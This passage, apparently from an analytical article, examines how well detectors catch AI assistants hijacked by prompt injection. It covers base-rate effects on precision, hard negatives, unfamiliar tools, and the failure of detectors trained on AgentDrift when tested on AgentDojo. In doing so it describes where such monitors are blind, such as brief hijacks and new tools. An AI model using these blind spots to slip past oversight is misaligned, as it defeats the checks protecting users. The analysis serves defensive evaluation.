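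The researchers built the trained detectors themselves, so these figures don't show how the published systems in their audit would perform.

### Twenty hijacks in 1,000 sessions

Let b be the base rate, r the recall and f the false-positive rate. Then

precision = b · r / (b · r + (1 − b) · f).

The numerator is the share of all sessions that are hijacked and flagged. The denominator is that share plus the share of all sessions that are harmless and flagged.

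Suppose a company checks 1,000 sessions with the combined detector, and 20 of them are hijacked. The detector flags 20 × 0.771, or about 15, of the hijacked sessions. It also flags 980 × 0.192, or about 188, of the harmless ones. Only 7.6% of the alerts are correct, so an analyst has to dismiss about 12 false alerts for each real one.

The detector's AUROC of 0.879 does not reflect this, because AUROC compares pairs of sessions, one hijacked and one normal, and so does not depend on how rare hijacks are.

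If one session in 1,000 is hijacked, the detector still produces about 192 false alerts and has a 77% chance of flagging the hijacked session. Precision falls to 0.4%, or roughly 250 false alerts for each hijack found.

On its clinic data, where about half the traces were abnormal, 96.7% of TraceAegis's alerts were correct. By the same calculation, with recall and the false-positive rate unchanged, about 37% would be correct if 2% of sessions were abnormal, and about 3% if one in 1,000 were.

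The argument comes from older work on programs that search computer logs for intruders. Axelsson (1999), in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and its Implications for the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, imagined a small site that produces a million log records a day and suffers two intrusions, each leaving traces in ten records. He grouped the records into 100,000 events of ten each. For two-thirds of its alarms to be real, even a detector that caught every intrusion could raise a false alarm on only about one event in 100,000. With false alarms on one event in 1,000, the site would get 100 false alarms a day and at most two real ones. Improving recall would hardly help, because nearly all the alarms come from harmless events.

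### Harmless sessions that look like attacks

A detector's false-positive rate also depends on which harmless sessions it examines. The combined detector flagged 11.8% of the ordinary sessions in AgentDrift but 38.7% of the hard negatives. With a base rate of 2%, its precision would be 11.7% if all the harmless sessions were ordinary and 3.9% if all were hard negatives. The 7.6% in the table reflects a mix in which 27% of the harmless sessions were hard negatives.

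Abbasi and colleagues therefore recommend that researchers state what kinds of harmless sessions they used to calculate any precision figure, and that they report the false-positive rate for each kind.

Pinjari and Saint-Germain used a language model to screen their data, and the hard negatives fooled it too. They also checked 1,200 traces by hand.

Recall varies with the kind of attack in a similar way. Pinjari and Saint-Germain tried a simple detector that used only surface features. It caught 88.0% of the hijacks in which every step after the injection served the attacker, but only 8.2% of those in which the assistant obeyed for a step or two and then went back to the user's task. A hijacked assistant that sends out a bank statement and then finishes the tenant's summary could be similarly hard to catch.

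### When half the tools are new

An assistant's tools change as users connect new services and vendors rename or replace tools. Abbasi and colleagues measure the effect on a detector with tool coverage, the share of the assistant's calls that go to tools in the detector's training data. If five of a session's ten calls go to a newly connected energy app and the other five go to tools from the training data, coverage is 50%.

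To lower the coverage without changing anything else, the researchers hid the names of randomly chosen tools from the trained detectors. The behaviour detector never uses tool names, so its AUROC stayed at 0.830. The combined detector started higher but lost its lead:

| Tool coverage | Behaviour detector | Combined detector |
|---|---|---|
| 100% | 0.830 | 0.879 |
| 78% | 0.830 | 0.853 |
| 48% | 0.830 | 0.825 |
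| 23% | 0.830 | 0.800 |
| 0% | 0.830 | 0.787 |

The sequence detector's score fell from 0.936 to 0.674, taking it from the best of the three detectors to the worst. A company whose tools were mostly new would have been wrong to choose it for its benchmark score.

The combined detector's score for a session is essentially a sum,

score = T + B,

where T comes from the tool counts and B from the summary measures. When every tool is new, all the counts are zero and T is the same for every session. It can't help to separate hijacked sessions from harmless ones, so only B can do that. B works less well than the behaviour detector's own score because training had fitted it to be used together with T. The constant T also happened to push sessions towards the "hijacked" side, so the false-positive rate rose from 19.2% to 65.7%.

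The sequence detector has an input reserved for unknown tools. The training data contained no unknown tools, so the detector never learned how to use that input. In the tests, the input caused the detector to flag more harmless sessions as hijacked, raising the false-positive rate from 4.5% to 73.7%.

Developers can largely fix the sequence detector's weakness on unfamiliar tools by retraining it. The researchers did this with a random fifth of the tool names replaced by "unknown". When every tool was new, the retrained detector's AUROC fell only to 0.794, and its false-positive rate stayed between 5% and 7%. It did no worse than before on familiar tools.

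Thresholds can still fail when an assistant starts a different kind of work. The researchers held out each of AgentDrift's five fields in turn, training the step detector on the other four and testing it on the one held out. The detector represents a tool's name by its meaning, so a new tool does not give it an untrained input. Even so, its false-positive rate rose from 0.1% to between 4.6% and 10.6% in medicine, coding and web browsing. Its recall fell to 34.5% in banking and 62.0% in email.

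New tasks and new people made little measurable difference as long as the tools stayed the same. When the researchers ran a similar test on AgentDojo's recorded sessions, the combined detector did not consistently do worse than the behaviour detector. The crossover at about half the calls comes from AgentDrift, whose five fields share no tools, so it could fall elsewhere in other data.

### From one benchmark to another

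Abbasi and colleagues next tested the AgentDrift-trained detectors on AgentDojo. They used recorded sessions from five models from 2024 and early 2025, with 2,294 successful hijacks and 392 harmless sessions.

| Detector | AUROC on AgentDojo after training on AgentDrift | AUROC on AgentDojo after training on AgentDojo |
|---|---|---|
| Behaviour | 0.482 | 0.741 |
| Combined | 0.473 | 0.797 |
| Sequence | 0.513 | 0.840 |
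| Step | 0.481 | 0.956 |
| Text | 0.520 | 0.996 |

None of the detectors trained on AgentDrift did better than chance (0.5). The combined detector flagged 22.4% of the harmless sessions and 22.5% of the hijacked ones. The same designs did much better when trained on other AgentDojo tasks (right-hand column), so AgentDojo's hijacks are detectable.

The text detector shows most clearly what the detectors learned in training instead. The prompts used to generate AgentDrift differed for each category of session, so the wording differed too. The number "2026", for example, appeared in 74% of the ordinary training sessions but in fewer than 5% of the hijacked ones, and the detector learned to treat it as strong evidence that a session was harmless. Removing all the digits barely changed its score on AgentDrift, because many other words also indicated the category.

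AgentDojo allows a different shortcut. Its attacks reuse a few fixed phrases, and five of them appear in 99.6% of the hijacked sessions and in none of the harmless ones. A search for those phrases scores 0.998. But they also appear in 94.7% of the sessions where the attack failed, so the search detects injection attempts whether or not they succeed.

Fomin (2026), in *When Benchmarks Lie*, found a related problem in classifiers that look for malicious prompts. Fomin, who works at the security company Zenity, combined 18 data sets and trained classifiers on the internal activity of language models. In standard tests, which used the same data sets as training, the classifier based on Llama 3.1 8B scored 0.996. When Fomin left each data set out of training in turn and tested on it, the score fell to 0.912. Across four models, the drop was 8.0 to 16.5 percentage points. Several of the data sets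 contained only attacks or only harmless prompts, so a classifier could label those prompts correctly just by recognising which data set they came from.

Fomin's classifiers stayed well above chance, unlike those of Abbasi and colleagues. This may be because Fomin trained on many sources at once. AgentDrift and AgentDojo also differ in several ways, including their tools, their attacks and what counts as a hijack, and the results don't show which difference caused the failure. Abbasi and colleagues tested transfer in only one direction, and GPT-4o produced 81% of the AgentDojo hijacks.

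### AlignmentCheck on both benchmarks

AlignmentCheck did work on AgentDojo, with an AUROC of 0.930 using Llama 3.3 70B and 0.934 using Claude Sonnet 5.5. Because it doesn't receive the tool results, it couldn't have relied on fixed phrases in an attacker's text. Abbasi and colleagues recorded their predictions for AlignmentCheck before running it, but did so only in part for the other detectors.

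A good ranking still did not guarantee useful alerts. AlignmentCheck flags a session if it objects to any step, with these results on AgentDojo:

| Model | Hijacked sessions flagged | Harmless sessions flagged | Precision if 2% of sessions are hijacked |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 90.0% | 17.3% | 9.6% |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 88.3% | 3.8% | 32.0% |

About a third of Claude's alerts would be correct, compared with one in ten of Llama's. The 95% confidence interval for Claude is wide, from 20% to 59%, because there were so few harmless sessions. Claude also flagged fewer failed attacks, 6.3% compared with Llama's 21.2%.

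Claude's advantage disappeared on AgentDrift, where it flagged 31.3% of the harmless sessions and its precision would be 5.4%. A provider that had tested Claude only on AgentDojo would have expected about two false alerts for each real one, but would have received about 17 on sessions like AgentDrift's.

Chennabasappa and colleagues had reported a false-positive rate below 4% on Meta's own scenarios, using a different model. They had also evaluated AlignmentCheck on AgentDojo, so its instructions may suit that benchmark unusually well. The October test left out PromptGuard 2, the classifier that LlamaFirewall runs alongside AlignmentCheck, and checked sessions only after they had ended. Meta's full system could therefore do better or worse than these figures.

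### What false-positive rate would be low enough?

The answer depends on what an alert triggers. If p is the precision a response needs, the precision formula gives the highest acceptable false-positive rate:

f = r · b / (1 − b) · (1 − p) / p.

In the earlier example of a £500 theft, holding an email was worthwhile once about 1% of alerts were correct, and turning the assistant off for a day was worthwhile once about 17% were. For alerts sent to a human analyst, a reasonable minimum is that half are correct. The table applies these three thresholds to a detector with a recall of 77.1%.

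| Response to an alert | Precision needed | Highest false-positive rate if 2% of sessions are hijacked | Highest false-positive rate if 0.1% are hijacked |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hold one email | About 1% | Any | 7.7% |
| Turn the assistant off for a day | About 17% | 7.9% | 0.4% |
| Have an analyst investigate | 50% | 1.6% | 0.08% |

The first entry is "any" because random alerts would already be correct 2% of the time. The sequence detector's 4.5% on familiar tools would be far too high for alerting an analyst. It would be low enough for holding an email at either base rate, but only if the detector could judge a session before the email left, which the study didn't test.

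Even 50% false alarms may be too many. A longer version of Axelsson's article, *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, draws on studies of operators in power stations, paper mills and similar plants, which suggest that most people would lose all faith in an alarm by the time half its warnings were false. Axelsson found no such experiments with security staff.

The classifier in *PromptShield* (Jacob, Alzahrani and colleagues, 2025) caught 65.3% of injections while flagging only 0.1% of harmless inputs. At the same false-positive rate, Meta's earlier PromptGuard caught 9.4%. But PromptShield classifies one input at a time, and an assistant that summarises a mailbox reads many. If PromptShield screened 20 harmless emails per session and its errors were independent, it would flag at least one email in about 2% of sessions.

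A low enough false-alert rate is also hard to prove. To show with 95% confidence that a detector flags fewer than 0.08% of harmless sessions, a tester would need to run it on roughly 3,900 harmless sessions without a single false alert. The October study had 392 such sessions from AgentDojo.

Nobody has measured the real base rate of attacks. It may be far below one in 1,000, since the companies that reported the Copilot leaks knew of no theft by a real attacker. If a company's staff start 200,000 sessions a day and one is hijacked, the false-positive rate can be no higher than about one in 260,000 for half the alerts to be correct.

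### A mailbox full of hard negatives

An assistant with access to someone's mail, files and history will have many harmless sessions that look like attacks. For example, a landlord asks for bank statements, an employer wants a form sent to a payroll company, or a bank asks its customer to confirm a payment. Citing the AgentDyn benchmark, Pinjari and Saint-Germain note that most instructions in other people's text are harmless and useful. Users often want the assistant to act on them, as when a tenant wants the bank statements sent to the landlord.

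The share of such sessions can change quickly. Suppose hard negatives normally make up 5% of the tenant's harmless sessions but rise to half while the tenant is moving house. If the combined detector flagged them at the same rate as AgentDrift's, its false-positive rate would rise from about 13% to 25%. With 20 sessions a day, the tenant would get five false alerts instead of two or three. The extra alerts would come while the tenant was sending documents to new addresses, so a real theft would be especially easy to overlook.

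The provider could not detect this change from tool coverage, which stays at 100% because the assistant uses the same mail search for the old landlord and the new one. The finding that new tasks and people cause little trouble is only limited reassurance, because AgentDrift's people are short profiles with a job, an employer and a few contacts, and a real person's correspondence varies much more.

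Real attackers also adapt, unlike those in the October study. Outsiders write part of what an assistant reads, so they can influence some of what a detector measures.

Abbasi and colleagues advise organisations to check a detector's threshold on their own sessions before trusting its alerts, which is harder for one person than for a company. The researchers reset thresholds using 200 unlabelled sessions from a field the detector hadn't seen. At 20 sessions a day, the tenant would need ten days to produce that many. Resetting the thresholds lowered the combined detector's average false-positive rate from over 50% to between 22% and 31%, still too high for most uses. When they set the sequence detector's threshold for a 2% base rate, it caught only 12% to 27% of the hijacks.
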